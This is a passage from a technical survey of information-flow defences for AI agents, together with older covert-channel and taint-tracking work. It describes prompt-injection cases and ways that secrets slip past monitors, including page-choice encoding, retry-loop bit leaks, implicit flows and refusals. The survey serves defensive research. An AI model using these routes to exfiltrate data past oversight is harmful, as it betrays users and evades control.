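Suppose that with one code an agent ends by naming page 7 in 50% of runs and page 2 in 30%, while the monitor stops the other 20%. With another code the figures are 40%, 50% and 10%. The smallest candidate for ω takes the larger figure for each page, 50% and 50%. These total 100%, so the two sets of figures are compatible, and the difference between them could come entirely from stopped runs. If instead no run stops and the figures are 50% and 50% for one code but 40% and 60% for the other, the larger figures total 110%, so the theorem rules this agent out.

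When every run finishes, compatible lists must be equal, and an outsider learns nothing from the results. When some runs stop early, the statistical distance between the lists (half the sum of their absolute differences) is at most the average of the two stopping probabilities. In the first example, both numbers are 15%. An operator could in principle measure how often runs stop and use the average to bound how much an outsider can learn from the results of completed runs.

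Garby and colleagues first tried a definition that compares only finished runs, but found it was wrong. For example, a program tosses a coin, and the monitor stops it if the coin shows heads and the secret is 1. Among the finished runs, heads turns up half the time if the secret is 0 and never if it is 1. These frequencies differ only because the monitor stopped some runs, and a termination-insensitive guarantee permits such differences. The program passes under the compatibility definition.

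The proof constructs ω by replacing every computation with a dummy value as soon as its label becomes secret. The altered program behaves identically for all secrets because it never reads them, and it reaches each public result at least as often as the real program does. Its results therefore provide a single ω that works for every secret. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, a proof assistant, and proved that their interpreter for the language produces results with the probabilities the theory assigns.

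The theorem assumes nothing about what the model writes, so even a fully compromised model can't write code that evades the labels. It does assume that whoever builds the tools labels data correctly at each source and puts a check at each sink. The theory also places all data inside the program and does not yet model live exchanges with outside services. It describes the results of a run, so it does not cover timing.

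### How far endorsement can weaken the guarantee

Strict labels would make some ordinary requests impossible. If a user asks an agent to pay a bill in a file, the account number comes from an untrusted source, so a payment tool that accepts only trusted input will reject it. The calculus therefore has an endorsement operation, which relabels untrusted data as trusted.

Endorsement changes only the integrity half of a label. If a program endorses a password, the result may count as trusted, but it stays secret. A second theorem, which Garby and colleagues also checked in Lean, shows that secrets can't influence public results, except through whether the program finishes. This holds however the program uses endorsement and whatever an attacker puts into the untrusted data.

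The program-counter label limits endorsement further. Code that the model writes after reading an untrusted web page runs in an untrusted context, and anything it endorses stays untrusted. This safeguard fails if an earlier step has already endorsed the page's text, because the code then runs in a trusted context. Garby and colleagues sketch a variant that marks endorsed data and blocks a second endorsement, but they have not yet formalized what it guarantees. An agent they wrote in the calculus was attacked in 1,296 benchmark runs and resisted in all but 2. Both failures involved endorsed data.

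For exfiltration, the harder case is an agent that has to release something private, such as the free slots in a calendar. That requires declassification, which lowers confidentiality instead of raising trust. The calculus can handle this by swapping the two halves of the label, but the second theorem would then protect integrity and would not limit which secrets the program declassifies.

### Two gaps in CaMeL's tracker

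In CaMeL, an earlier design, a model writes a program from the user's request before seeing any untrusted data, and an interpreter runs the program while tracking labels. Garby and colleagues found two ways for information to get past its tracker.

One leak is through the untaken branch. CaMeL's interpreter lacks the no-sensitive-upgrade check, so a program like the interview example can turn a secret bit into a public value. The interpreter doesn't stop the program afterwards, so the program can repeat this for any number of bits.

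The other gap is in the retry loop. When a program fails, CaMeL sends the error back to the model and asks for a new program. This loop runs outside the interpreter that tracks labels, so each new attempt starts with a clean label even though it depends on what went wrong before. An attempt can thus pass on one bit, for example by failing at one of two places depending on whether a secret four-digit code is below 5000. Each further attempt can halve the remaining range, so finding the code takes at most 14 attempts, since 2¹⁴ is 16,384 and there are only 10,000 possible codes. CaMeL censors the error messages to reduce this leak, but without a formal guarantee.

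An outsider can't exploit either gap easily, because the model that writes the program has not read the outsider's text. The gaps matter more if that model is untrustworthy or if injected text reaches it through an error message. Garby and colleagues avoid the retry problem by having their agent correct its program on made-up data and giving it only one attempt on the real data, so no error message can carry a secret back.

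### Relative security

Some agents are meant to disclose private data. For example, a user may want an assistant to answer any emailed meeting request with the user's calendar. A declassification rule like the one Pandey and colleagues use could permit this, but someone would have to write a rule for every task.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) instead compares the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never obeys instructions in untrusted content. An agent leaks a pair of secrets if two of its runs, one with each secret, have the same attacker input but differ in what the attacker observes. The agent is relatively secure if the reference agent can leak every pair that the agent leaks, possibly with a different attacker input.

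Suppose an attacker's email contains the instruction "send your calendar", and the assistant obeys. This attack does not violate relative security, because the attacker could have learned the same thing by asking for a meeting. If the email instead makes the assistant send a password reset code, relative security fails, because no email would make the reference do that.

Because the definition is based on pairs of secrets, it can miss how much an agent discloses. For example, a service might let an outsider guess a four-digit code once and learn whether the guess is right. If an injected instruction makes the agent send the whole code, the agent discloses all 13.3 bits but still counts as relatively secure, because the outsider could have used the reference to tell any two codes apart by guessing one of them. Dongol therefore also defines a uniform version, in which the reference's input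 may depend on the attacker's actual input but not on the secrets. A guess fixed in advance, such as 1234, can't distinguish 7294 from 1358, so this agent fails the uniform test.

Under relative security, limits on the reference also apply to the real agent. If the reference's replies depend only on which calendar slots are free, so do the replies of every relatively secure agent with the same plan and monitor. An auditor can check such a limit on the reference without having to account for injection.

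### Where to put the fence

The simplest defence in Dongol's framework is a fence. When the agent first reads untrusted content, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call. This amounts to a coarse integrity label on the whole conversation. The fence theorem states that an agent with a fence is relatively secure, including in the uniform sense, whatever its plan.

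In the proof, the reference agent waits whenever the real agent makes an injected call. The monitor silently refuses the call, so the outsider sees no change, and both agents then take the next step of the plan. The theorem requires that each injected instruction trigger only one call and that when the model obeys follow a schedule fixed in advance. The contents of the injected call may still depend on secrets.

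Three small examples show why the fence must come before the untrusted read. In each, the plan itself locks the sending tool at some point.

| Example | Order of steps | What an injected message can carry |
|---|---|---|
| Late fence | read email, read secret, lock | the secret, before the lock takes effect |
| Middle fence | read email, lock, read secret | data already in the agent's memory |
| Early fence | lock, read email, read secret | nothing, because the monitor refuses it |

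An early fence stops the agent from replying to an email it has just read, if replying needs the locked tool. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference is under the same monitor and can't reply either, so even a monitor that refuses every call satisfies the definition.

An agent that handles one email after another needs its tools back at some point. If the monitor returns them while an old email is still in the conversation, the model may then obey instructions in that email. Returning them only when the conversation is empty is safe, as long as the model doesn't keep obeying injected instructions forever. An instruction stored in long-term memory survives clearing the conversation, so the monitor has to treat loading that memory as another untrusted read.

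### The 25 verdicts and their scope

Dongol used Isabelle/HOL, another proof assistant, to check verdicts on 25 small example agents. Ten are secure, nine leak, and for the other six the verdict depends on factors such as what the outsider can see. Most of the secure verdicts cover only the attack in the example, so they show what the definition accepts rather than how well a defence works in general.

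One of the nine leaks is an implicit flow of the kind explicit secrecy permits. A model without tools reads an attacker's message along with the user's private notes, and the plan sends an outsider 1 or 0 depending on the model's answer. Both numbers are public constants, so every message passes a check on data labels. But an injected instruction can make the answer depend on the notes, and the outsider then learns one bit about them. Dongol modelled CaMeL's normal mode. CaMeL's strict mode, which labels values according to the conditions that led to them, should address this case, but Dongol has not analysed it.

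Approvals give a subtler example. If the user approves the sending tool for one message, an injected call can use the approval first and send private data. If the user instead approves the exact text, the injected call goes through only when the private data matches the approved reply, which the outsider would receive anyway. In that case the reply arrives one step early, so an outsider who can time messages learns whether the two texts match.

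Tools that are each safe alone can be insecure in combination. In Dongol's example, an agent that can only read the inbox or only fetch web pages leaks nothing, but an agent with both tools does leak. Removing a tool can also make a secure agent insecure, because the reference loses the tool too and may no longer be able to make the disclosure that justified the agent's own disclosure.

The fence theorem assumes an outsider who sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. It also compares only runs in which the outsider receives the same number of messages between one untrusted read and the next. It can therefore miss a leak in which a secret determines whether the agent sends a message at all. For example, suppose the monitor lets the agent fetch only one approved newsletter. An injected instruction could make the agent fetch the newsletter if a secret is 0 and otherwise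 try a forbidden page, which the monitor blocks. The outsider sees one request in the first case and none in the second, so the theorem does not compare the two runs.

The framework excludes search engines and other tools whose answers depend on the request, if an attacker could control those answers. More importantly, it excludes agents whose model chooses every call, as in the ordinary agent loop, where the model sees each result before choosing the next call. Such an agent has no plan before it reads untrusted content, so there is no reference agent to compare it with.

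## Theory: limiting the total information that many small disclosures carry

Costa and colleagues permit implicit flows because they expect an outsider to learn only a little from an agent's choices. Information theory can measure the amount in bits. A monitor can then add up the bits from each disclosure and stop the agent before the total does harm. This limit on the total is called a leakage budget.

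### Measuring a leak in bits

The entropy of a secret measures how uncertain an outsider is about it. If the secret S has the value s with probability p(s), its entropy is

H(S) = −Σ p(s) log₂ p(s).

For a random four-digit code this is log₂(10,000), or about 13.3 bits. A code that a person picked has less entropy, because some codes are more popular than others. After the outsider has observed an output Y, the uncertainty H(S | Y) remains. The mutual information

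I(S; Y) = H(S) − H(S | Y)

is the average number of bits that the output reveals.

When the agent spells out the code 7294 in four page visits, each visit leaves only a tenth of the codes that were still possible, and the 3.3 bits per visit add up to the whole code. In general, leaks in a sequence add up according to the chain rule:

I(S; Y₁, Y₂) = I(S; Y₁) + I(S; Y₂ | Y₁).

The last term counts only what the second output adds to the first, so repeating a message reveals nothing new.

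Noise makes each output less informative. Suppose that half of the agent's visits, chosen at random, go to a random page for unrelated reasons, and that the outsider can't tell which ones. Each visit then reveals about 0.9 bits. This is also the channel's capacity, the most information per use that any encoding of the secret could achieve. The agent now needs at least about 15 visits to send the code reliably, instead of four.

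### When one guess is enough

Mutual information is an average, so it can hide a serious leak. The computer scientist Geoffrey Smith made this objection in 2009, when most researchers in the field were using Shannon's entropy. He was concerned with attackers who need to guess a secret correctly only once. In an example similar to his, two agents know a random four-digit code. Agent A sends an outsider the whole code if it ends in 0, and otherwise sends a fixed greeting. Agent B always reveals which quarter of the range from 0000 to 9999 contains the code.

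| | Agent A | Agent B |
|---|---|---|
| Mutual information | 1.47 bits | 2 bits |
| Outsider's chance of guessing the code in one try | 10.01% | 0.04% |
| Min-entropy leakage | 9.97 bits | 2 bits |

By mutual information, agent B is the worse of the two, yet agent A gives the outsider a chance 250 times as good. Smith therefore preferred min-entropy, which depends only on the probability of the best guess. The leakage is

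log₂(chance of a correct guess afterwards ÷ chance beforehand).

If an outsider can distinguish at most n outcomes, neither of the two measures can exceed log₂(n). Disclosures limited to b bits can therefore multiply the chance of a correct guess by at most 2ᵇ. With a limit of eight bits, the chance of guessing the four-digit code rises from 0.01% to at most 2.56%. A random 128-bit key would still be practically impossible to guess.

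### Metering what an agent reads and sends

Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026), in *L3M*, describe a leakage budget for a system that runs many agents. It is a design, which the released version of the system does not include. The meter would work as follows:

1. All stored data carries a label for its kind, such as "payroll".
2. When an agent reads data of kind K, the meter adds the number of bytes to a total called ingress(K), which never goes down.
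3. When the agent sends a message, the meter adds the message's full length to egress(K) for every kind K that the agent holds. It charges the full length because the agent could hide a secret in any byte.
4. The leak of kind K is at most the smaller of the two totals, min(ingress(K), egress(K)).
5. A separate gate compares the totals with a limit and can refuse further actions.

Suppose an agent holds 64 secret bytes and sends two requests of 50 bytes each. It has sent 100 bytes, but it can have leaked at most min(64, 100) = 64 secret bytes. The meter has to take the minimum once, over the totals. If it took the minimum for each request and added the results, it would get 50 + 50 = 100, which is more than the 64 secret bytes the agent holds.

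The ingress limit follows from the data-processing inequality, a theorem that processing data can't add information about its source. What the agent sends can depend on the secret only through what it has read, so the limit holds even if the agent encrypts the secret, splits it up or conveys it through choices. For example, an agent that has read the code 7294 from a file has taken in four bytes, so its page visits can reveal at most 32 bits about the code. This is more than the 13.3 bits the code actually carries, but the limit covers a channel that a check on the labels of the arguments could miss.

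The guarantee is almost worthless for a short secret, though, since the four bytes are the whole code. A limit protects a secret only if it allows out less data than the secret contains, and a three-byte cap would stop the agent from requesting any web page after reading the code. Limits are better suited to large datasets, such as source code or payroll records, where losing a few hundred bytes may be tolerable. For a short secret such as a password, an agent that doesn't need it should not be able to read it.

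The meter also has to follow data between agents, or an agent could pass a secret to a second agent whose totals are still zero. In the L3M design, every message between agents counts, and the receiver inherits the sender's labels. Suppose a parent agent gives a child agent 10 bytes of payroll data, and the child reads another 90 and returns a 500-byte report. The meter adds 90 bytes to the parent's total, because the report can't contain more than 90 bytes of payroll data beyond what the parent supplied. Each stored file has a record of the bytes counted for it, tied to a hash (a short fingerprint) of its contents. If someone swaps the contents, the hash no longer matches, and the meter counts the file's full size under the strictest label.

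### Channels that escape the meter

The bound holds only if the meter covers every channel. In the L3M design, data that arrives by an unrecognized route gets the strictest label, so a forgotten rule makes the meter count too much. But a meter that counts bytes can still miss information conveyed by something other than the bytes themselves.

Eisenach and colleagues show this with two agents that communicate only by mail. One can read a company's private source code but has no network access, while the other can search the web but can't read the code. If the first agent sends a single letter, padded to a fixed length of k bytes, nothing the second agent does online can reveal more than 8k bits about the source code. Without padding, the first agent could also send information through the letter's length. If it chooses when to write or how many letters to send, those choices also carry information,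 so the operator has to count that information toward the limit or fix the timing and number of letters in advance.

The egress total doesn't count information conveyed by silence. If an agent messages a colleague only when the user's calendar contains no job interview, its silence reveals the interview while egress stays at zero. The ingress limit still holds because it restricts what the agent knows, however the agent communicates.

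### Fixed menus and typed answers

A system can also restrict what an agent can send. In another L3M example, an agent without secrets prepares a list of N options, and an agent with secrets picks one. The choice reveals at most log₂(N) bits, or one byte for a list of 256, however much private data the agent used to make it. If the options contain anything derived from the secrets, their text also counts toward the total disclosed.

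Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, applies the same reasoning to tool calls. A gate lets the model use only a declared set D of capabilities, such as reading files or accessing the network, and refuses everything else. Each call then has |D| + 1 possible outcomes, where the extra one is the refusal, so it carries at most

log₂(|D| + 1) bits.

With ten capabilities this is about 3.5 bits per call. Over eight calls there are 11⁸ possible sequences, roughly 214 million, so the limit is 27.7 bits, about twice what the four-digit code requires. A bigger problem is that the formula ignores the arguments of each call. An agent with network access could put the whole code into one web address. The menu limits what an outsider can learn only if it lists complete calls, including their arguments.

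FIDES, the agent system that Costa and colleagues built, makes the size of an answer part of its label. The agent can ask a separate model without tools to read restricted text and reply in a prescribed format. FIDES orders the formats by how much information they can hold:

yes/no ⊑ choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text.

A policy can then accept a yes/no answer where it would reject free text from the same source. For example, it may let a yes/no answer drawn from an untrusted email influence an important action, because the email's author controls only one bit. The same mechanism can also release one bit about private data.

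One bit is harmless only if the agent can't keep asking. By halving the range each time, 14 yes/no answers identify any four-digit code, just as repeated attempts did in CaMeL's retry loop. The label can't reflect this. Under the join rule,

yes/no ⊔ yes/no = yes/no,

even though two answers can carry two bits. The same holds in every lattice, since joining a label with itself leaves it unchanged. A system that wants to limit repeated answers therefore needs a counter in addition to its labels.

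How much the counter should add for each answer depends on which questions the attacker can ask. Clark, Hunt and Malacaria point out that even a failed password attempt leaks some information, because it slightly narrows the attacker's search. For a random four-digit code, checking one guess reveals about 0.0015 bits on average, and 14 wrong guesses rule out only 14 of the 10,000 codes. Adding a full bit per answer is therefore far too much if the service answers only "is this the code?", but it is right if the attacker can ask any yes/no question, since each answer could halve the remaining possibilities.

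### Earlier limits on covert channels and network traffic

Security engineers have long set limits of this kind. According to DST Group, an Australian defence research organization, academic work on covert channels began with Butler Lampson's observation that programs can communicate by manipulating shared resources or the timing of events. Under the US Defense Department's 1985 evaluation criteria, known as the Orange Book, covert channels below one bit per second were acceptable in most settings, and rates above 100 bits per second were considered high. Systems were also expected to be able to audit channels faster than one bit in ten seconds. At one bit per second, a large archive would take a long time to steal, but the four-digit code would take only 14 seconds and a 128-bit key about two minutes.

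Later work measured ordinary network traffic. Filters that search outgoing data for known confidential text can't identify encrypted or disguised leaks, so Borders and Prakash, in *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP*, proposed measuring the maximum information the traffic could carry. They continued this work in *Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (2009). Most of what a browser sends is repeated, or follows from the web protocol or earlier server messages, so a monitor can subtract it. On real browsing traffic, the algorithms discounted 98.5% of the bytes, according to Borders's patent application, *Method, system and computer program product for comparing or measuring information content*. An agent's traffic may be harder to discount because the agent writes its own search queries and can compose addresses that don't appear on any page.

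Paxson, Christodorescu and colleagues (2013) tested such a limit at a much larger scale in *Practical Comprehensive Bounds on Surreptitious Communication Over DNS*. Computers use DNS to look up the network address for a name such as example.com. An attacker who runs the name server for a domain sees lookups of names within it, so a compromised computer can send the attacker data by looking up chosen names. It could send one bit a day by looking up either "www" or "mail" in the attacker's domain, and nobody could recognize the leak from a single lookup.

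Paxson and colleagues' detector groups a day's lookups by computer and by domain. It compresses the sequence of names, the sequence of query types and the intervals between lookups, then adds up the compressed sizes. Because the compression is lossless, the total can't be smaller than the information in the sequences, apart from timing differences finer than 10 milliseconds. The intervals are counted because they alone could carry 108 kilobytes a day, given one lookup per second and a clock accurate to a millisecond. When the researchers sent files through four kinds of test channel, the detector's estimates were 5 to 11% above the true size.

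An analyst has to inspect every domain that could have received more than 4 kilobytes from one computer in a day. Three sites had records detailed enough to test this as intended:

| Site | Days of data | Domains flagged | Confirmed DNS tunnels | New domains flagged in a typical week |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Industrial research laboratory | 1,212 | 362 | 0 | 2.0 |
| National laboratory | 2,565 | 433 | 2 | 1.1 |
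| Supercomputer centre | 1,642 | 38 | 0 | 0.15 |

Only two of the 833 flagged domains were confirmed tunnels, and staff had set up both to get free internet access at Wi-Fi hotspots. Four others involved malware, and most of the rest were harmless services or misconfigured computers. The weekly workload stayed small because the detector doesn't flag a domain again once an analyst has checked it. Simply adding up the lengths of all the names looked up would have raised 200 times as many alerts. Paxson and colleagues also found 57 tunnels in traffic pooled from many networks, using a threshold of 10 kilobytes.

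Four kilobytes a day is a loose limit for credentials, since it lets through 256 keys of 128 bits. At the industrial laboratory, lowering the threshold to 256 bytes would have given analysts about 50 times as many domains to inspect and would still have let 16 keys through. The limit also applies to each computer and domain separately, so an attacker with ten domains could receive ten times as much without an alert, and using several compromised computers would raise the total further.

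### When a refusal gives the secret away

A monitor that enforces a limit must sometimes refuse, and a refusal can reveal a secret, just as silencing the scheduling assistant can. Database researchers studied this problem for systems that answer questions about private records. Suppose an assistant may state the highest of several sealed bids but must never reveal any particular company's bid. An outsider asks for the highest bid among companies A, B and C, and the assistant answers 5 million. The outsider then asks for the highest bid among A and B. If that is also 5 million, the assistant can safely answer. If it is lower, answering would reveal that C bid 5 million, so the assistant refuses. But an outsider who knows this rule can infer C's bid from the refusal.

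Krishnaram Kenthapadi, Nina Mishra and Kobbi Nissim proposed simulatable auditing as a remedy in 2005. The monitor decides whether to refuse using only the new question and the earlier questions and answers, without looking at the true answer. In the example, it refuses the second question whatever the bids are, because some bids consistent with the first answer would make the second answer revealing. The outsider could have predicted the refusal, so learns nothing from it. However, the monitor also refuses questions it could have answered safely.

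A leakage budget can have the same flaw. If its limit depends on how much secret data the agent has read, a sudden refusal may show an outsider that the agent has opened a long file. A similar problem arises if the budget counts the information in a message instead of its length. Eisenach and colleagues suggest measuring messages by their compressed size, so that standard phrases would use little of the budget, but then when the budget runs out depends on what the messages contain.

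The damage is smaller if the first refusal closes the channel permanently. Suppose an agent is due to send 100 messages whose content and timing are fixed in advance. The outsider can observe only where the sequence stops, if it does. There are 101 possible outcomes, so they carry at most 6.7 bits. If the monitor blocks single messages and lets the agent continue, each message can be present or missing, and the pattern can carry 100 bits.

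### Budgets over long runs

Small budgets don't last long when an agent works for hours or days. Suppose an operator lets an agent send 1,000 bytes a day after it has read a payroll file. If the meter counts every byte of a web address and each address is 60 bytes long, the agent can make 16 requests a day. After that, the operator has to stop the agent, ask a person to approve every further request, or raise the limit. A fixed menu makes the budget last longer, but each visit to one of ten pages still uses 3.3 bits, so an allowance of 100 bits runs out after 30 visits.

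Resetting the budget every day lets the agent keep working but turns a limit on the total into a limit on the rate. Even at one bit per day, an outsider could receive the four-digit code in two weeks. Changing the code every week would help. Seven bits raise the chance of guessing it in one try to at most 128 in 10,000, and each change makes what the outsider has learned useless. Payroll records and source code can't be replaced this way, so the leaks from successive days add up.

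## Deployed systems: the record of labels in operating systems and browsers

Operating systems were using labels to track data before Denning published the lattice model. In the late 1960s, ADEPT-50, a military time-sharing system, raised the label on a running job whenever the job accessed more sensitive data. Browser makers later took a simpler approach and separated websites from one another. Engineers have since measured the overhead of both approaches, and attackers and researchers have found leaks in both.

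### Reading up and writing down

Most labelled operating systems follow a model that David Bell and Leonard LaPadula developed in the 1970s. Every process (a running program) and every file has a security level. The level consists of a rank, such as "secret" or "top secret", and a set of categories, such as "nuclear" or "crypto". One level dominates another if its rank is at least as high and its categories include all of the other's. The model has two main rules:

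1. A process may read a file only if the process's level dominates the file's.
2. If a process can read file A and modify file B, then the level of B must dominate the level of A.

People often shorten these to "no read up" and "no write down". The second rule, which Bell and LaPadula called the star property, deals with sequences of actions. Suppose an officer cleared for secret nuclear files opens one in a text editor that contains hidden malicious code. Ordinary permissions let the editor read the file and write to a public folder, because the officer may do both. The star property forbids the combination. Efstathopoulos, Krohn and colleagues, in *Labels and Event Processes in the Asbestos Operating System*, point out that without it, the file's secrecy would depend on how the program behaved.

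Useful work sometimes requires moving information to a lower secrecy level, for example to publish part of a secret report. Under the model, only specially privileged users can do this. Military systems also had a fixed set of ranks and categories, which a security administrator assigned. A web server couldn't create a category for each of its customers, so the labels were of little use to ordinary applications. Three research systems of the 2000s removed that restriction.

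### Asbestos: any program can create a label

In Asbestos (2005), any process can create a new category, and whoever creates it may remove it from data or pass that right to another process. No administrator is involved. Each process P has a send label, Pₛ, which records what it has been exposed to, and a receive label, Pᵣ, which sets the most it may accept. Leaving aside the special rights of owners, P may send a message to Q only if

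Pₛ ⊑ Qᵣ,

and when the message arrives, Q's send label becomes

Qₛ ⊔ Pₛ.

If one web server process serves Alice and then Bob, it ends up with both users' labels and can no longer reply to either of them. Asbestos therefore lets a process split into "event processes", one for each user's session, each with its own labels and private memory. This took about 6 kilobytes of extra memory per session.

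The labels themselves were the larger source of overhead. With one stored session, the Asbestos server handled more requests per second than Apache, a standard web server, did when it started a new program for every request. With 10,000 sessions, it handled about half as many as Apache. At that size, some trusted components that dealt with every user had labels with more than 20,000 entries, and the kernel (the core of the operating system) spent much of its time checking them.

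Efstathopoulos and colleagues also had to stop the label checks themselves from leaking information. When a process sends a message in Asbestos, the kernel may report success even if it has discarded the message. Otherwise a program could signal a 1 by arranging for a delivery to succeed and a 0 by arranging for it to fail. A leak remains, however. Suppose two harmless processes, B₀ and B₁, each send a regular signal to an outside program. A process holding a secret bit sends a message to one of them, chosen according to the bit. The recipient acquires the secret label, so the kernel discards its signals, and which signal has stopped reveals the bit to the outside program. Efstathopoulos and colleagues consider such channels inherent in any system that checks labels at run time and lets them change.

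### HiStar: confining a virus scanner

HiStar (2006) closes part of this gap by never raising a label automatically. A thread (one strand of a running program) has to request a more restrictive label before it can read more sensitive data. Apart from categories that the thread T owns, it may read an object O only if

L(O) ⊑ L(T),

and may modify O only if L(T) ⊑ L(O) holds as well.

In *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar*, Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and colleagues explain the design using the example of a virus scanner. The scanner has to read all of a user's private files, and a separate program has to contact the internet for updates. On Linux, a compromised scanner could leave private data in the shared folder for temporary files. The update program, if also compromised, could read that data and send it out through the content, order or timing of its update requests. Scanning a file,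 writing a temporary file and requesting updates are all normal actions for these programs, so this is the same kind of leak as one through an agent's page visits.

On HiStar, the user starts the scanner through a 110-line program called wrap, which creates a new category, v, and attaches it to the scanner. Anything the scanner writes, and any helper program it starts, also carries v. The kernel blocks every transfer from anything carrying v to the network or the update program. Only wrap can remove v, which it does to show the user the scanner's report. As long as wrap and the kernel are correct, a fault in the scanner's more than 40,000 lines of code can't send the files out, except through covert channels.

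Even so, HiStar had to release some information. A Unix program is normally notified when a program it started has finished, and that notification reveals something about what happened inside. HiStar's library can release three kinds of event from a confined program: that it has exited, that it needs more storage, and that it has created a file. The third reveals the most because it includes the file's name. For the virus scanner, wrap allows none of these releases and kills the scanner after a set time, to limit how much it could leak through covert channels. Zeldovich and colleagues write that they don't know how to solve timing channels, because network services have to respond quickly and an outsider can measure small delays.

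### Flume: labels for an existing wiki

Krohn, Yip and colleagues (2007), in *Information Flow Control for Standard OS Abstractions*, brought the idea to Linux. Their system, Flume, attaches tags to processes and files. For each tag t there are two rights: t⁺ allows a process to add the tag to its own label, and t⁻ allows it to remove the tag. To protect his files, Bob creates a tag b and gives everyone b⁺ but keeps b⁻ for one trusted program. Any text editor can then open the files, subject to four conditions:

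1. If the editor reads Bob's files, it carries b.
2. While it carries b, it can write only to processes and files that also carry b.
3. It can't remove b.
4. While it carries b, it can't use the network.

Denning's transitivity argument then applies to long sequences of transfers. Each transfer can pass Bob's data only to something else tagged b, so no chain of untrusted programs can carry the data to the network.

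Krohn and colleagues tested Flume on MoinMoin, a wiki with 91,000 lines of code. The original program checked reading permissions in 41 places and writing permissions in 19, and a single missing check could expose a private page. In the Flume version, a small launcher sets the labels and then starts the wiki, which doesn't need to be trusted. Two known bugs that let users bypass the permissions remained in the code but no longer revealed private data. The work also exposed an undocumented leak in the original wiki, where Bob could try to create a page called "ReasonsToFireBob" and learn from the failure that a secret page of that name already existed.

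| System | Code that has to be correct | Changes to applications | Measured cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Asbestos | Kernel and the web server's shared components, but not the programs for individual services | A rebuilt version of an existing web server | 6 KB of memory per session; slower as sessions accumulate |
| HiStar | Kernel of under 16,000 lines, plus small programs such as wrap | Little or none for many Unix programs | Virus scan as fast as on Linux; compiling the kernel took 6.2 seconds instead of 4.7 |
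| Flume | All of Linux, Flume's monitor and a launcher of about 1,000 lines | About 1,000 of the wiki's 91,000 lines | 43% fewer page views and 34% fewer edits per second |

The wiki also lost some features, including its index and its hit counters. These features collect information from many pages in shared files, so Flume treated them as attempted leaks and blocked them. Krohn and colleagues could have restored them with programs that had the right to remove tags, but ran out of time. Like the wiki's index, an agent's long-term memory and its logs collect data from many sources in one place, so someone has to decide what may come out again.

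All three systems remained research projects. Mainstream operating systems offer labels, for example in SELinux, an extension of Linux, but an administrator sets the policy and ordinary applications can't add their own labels.

### TaintDroid: following data inside apps

Labels on whole processes are too coarse for a phone app that legitimately uses both the user's location and the internet. *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert and colleagues, 2010) followed the data inside the app instead. It modified Android so that location, camera, microphone and address-book data, text messages, the phone number and the device's identifiers carried labels from the moment an app received them. Because Android ran apps through an interpreter, TaintDroid could attach a label to every variable and combine the labels at each operation. Each message between apps and each stored file had a single label. When labelled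 data reached the network, TaintDroid recorded the app, the kind of data and the destination, but did not block the transmission.

The team tested 30 apps, chosen at random from 358 popular ones that could use the internet and also location, camera or audio data. They used each app by hand, for a little over 100 minutes in total. Of 1,130 network connections, TaintDroid flagged 105. The researchers judged 37 of these clearly legitimate, such as requests for a map of the user's surroundings. The other 68 came from 20 apps:

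| What the app sent | Apps |
|---|---|
| Location, to advertising servers | 15 |
| Device identifier, to the app's own server | 7 |
| Phone number and SIM card identifiers, to the app's own server | 2 |

(Three apps appear in more than one row.) Users had granted the permissions involved, but could not tell from them that the app would combine access to location with access to the internet in this way. Some of the location data was sent in a binary format that a search for recognizable coordinates would have missed. A manual check of the messages TaintDroid flagged found no false positives, but nobody could check how many leaks it had missed, since the apps' source code was not available.

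The 37 legitimate flags are as informative as the other 68 because they show that a tracker can establish which server received location data, but not whether it should have. Enck and colleagues had to decide that by hand, using the server's name, the log and whatever the app had told its users.

Tracking slowed a test of pure computation by 14% and communication between apps by 27%. A later paper, also titled *TaintDroid*, reports a 32% slowdown for computation. It also describes a second round of tests in 2012, in which a similar share of apps potentially misused private data.

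### The decision to ignore implicit flows

Enck and colleagues designed TaintDroid to track only explicit flows, for practical reasons. Tracking implicit flows fully requires analyzing the program's text, and the apps came without source code. A partial analysis while the app ran would have slowed it down and caused false alarms. Enck and colleagues acknowledged that a truly malicious app could therefore get private data past the tracker. Golam Sarwar and colleagues confirmed this in 2013 with test apps that evaded the tracker in several ways.

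Enck and colleagues argued, in partial answer, that an app contains strange code if it deliberately encodes data in choices instead of copying it directly. Another tool might detect that code as a sign of bad intent. This argument is reasonable for apps but doesn't apply to agents. When an agent visits pages 7, 2, 9 and 4 to spell out a secret code, there is no suspicious program to inspect. The decision happens inside the model, and an injected instruction that caused it may have been on a web page that has since changed.

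TaintDroid also loses the label on data that leaves the phone and later returns in a server's reply. This matters more for agents than it did for phones, because agents routinely store data on remote services and read it back. If an agent saves credentials in an online document and reads the document the next day, the credentials will come back unlabelled unless the document service stores the label or the operator treats everything from that service as secret.

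### When nearly everything becomes tainted

Too many labels can be as bad as too few. TaintDroid put a single label on a 15-digit SIM card identifier that contains a country code, a network code and the subscriber's own number. Android uses the two codes as settings in many unrelated messages, so the label spread to everything in those messages and then further. Enck and colleagues had to switch off tracking for this identifier during their tests.

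The problem is worse for trackers that cover a whole computer, including the operating system. Consider a program that turns a keystroke into a letter by looking it up in a table:

`letter := table[key]`

When a system converts a keystroke to a letter by looking it up in a table, the letter comes from the table, which is public. A tracker that follows only copies will therefore leave the letter unlabelled and miss a program that steals passwords as the user types. The tracker can instead label the result of a lookup whenever the position in the table is secret, a method called pointer tainting. Asia Slowinska and Herbert Bos argued in 2009 that this method causes false alarms. An operating system performs such lookups constantly, and once a label reaches the positions that the system uses to find its own records, it spreads to unrelated data until the tracker can't distinguish a keystroke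 logger from any other program.

*Tainting is not pointless* (2010) answered that many of these objections apply only to analysing malicious software, and that pointer tainting remains promising against attacks that corrupt a program's memory. Slowinska and Bos (2010) replied with *Pointer Tainting Still Pointless*, subtitled "But We All See the Point of Tainting", so the dispute was over pointer tainting and not taint tracking in general. The first paper's defence of pointer tainting is of little help against data exfiltration, because it gives up on using the technique to catch software that steals private data.

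The choice channel has the same form:

`page := pages[digit]`

Sixteen years after that dispute, agent designers face the same decision about whether to keep the label when they store tool results in variables and let the model choose among them.

Speed has improved more than accuracy. Trackers that follow every machine instruction typically slow a program about tenfold. *Minemu* (Bosman, Slowinska and Bos, 2011) reduced the slowdown to between 1.5 and 3 times for real applications by using an emulator designed specifically for tracking.

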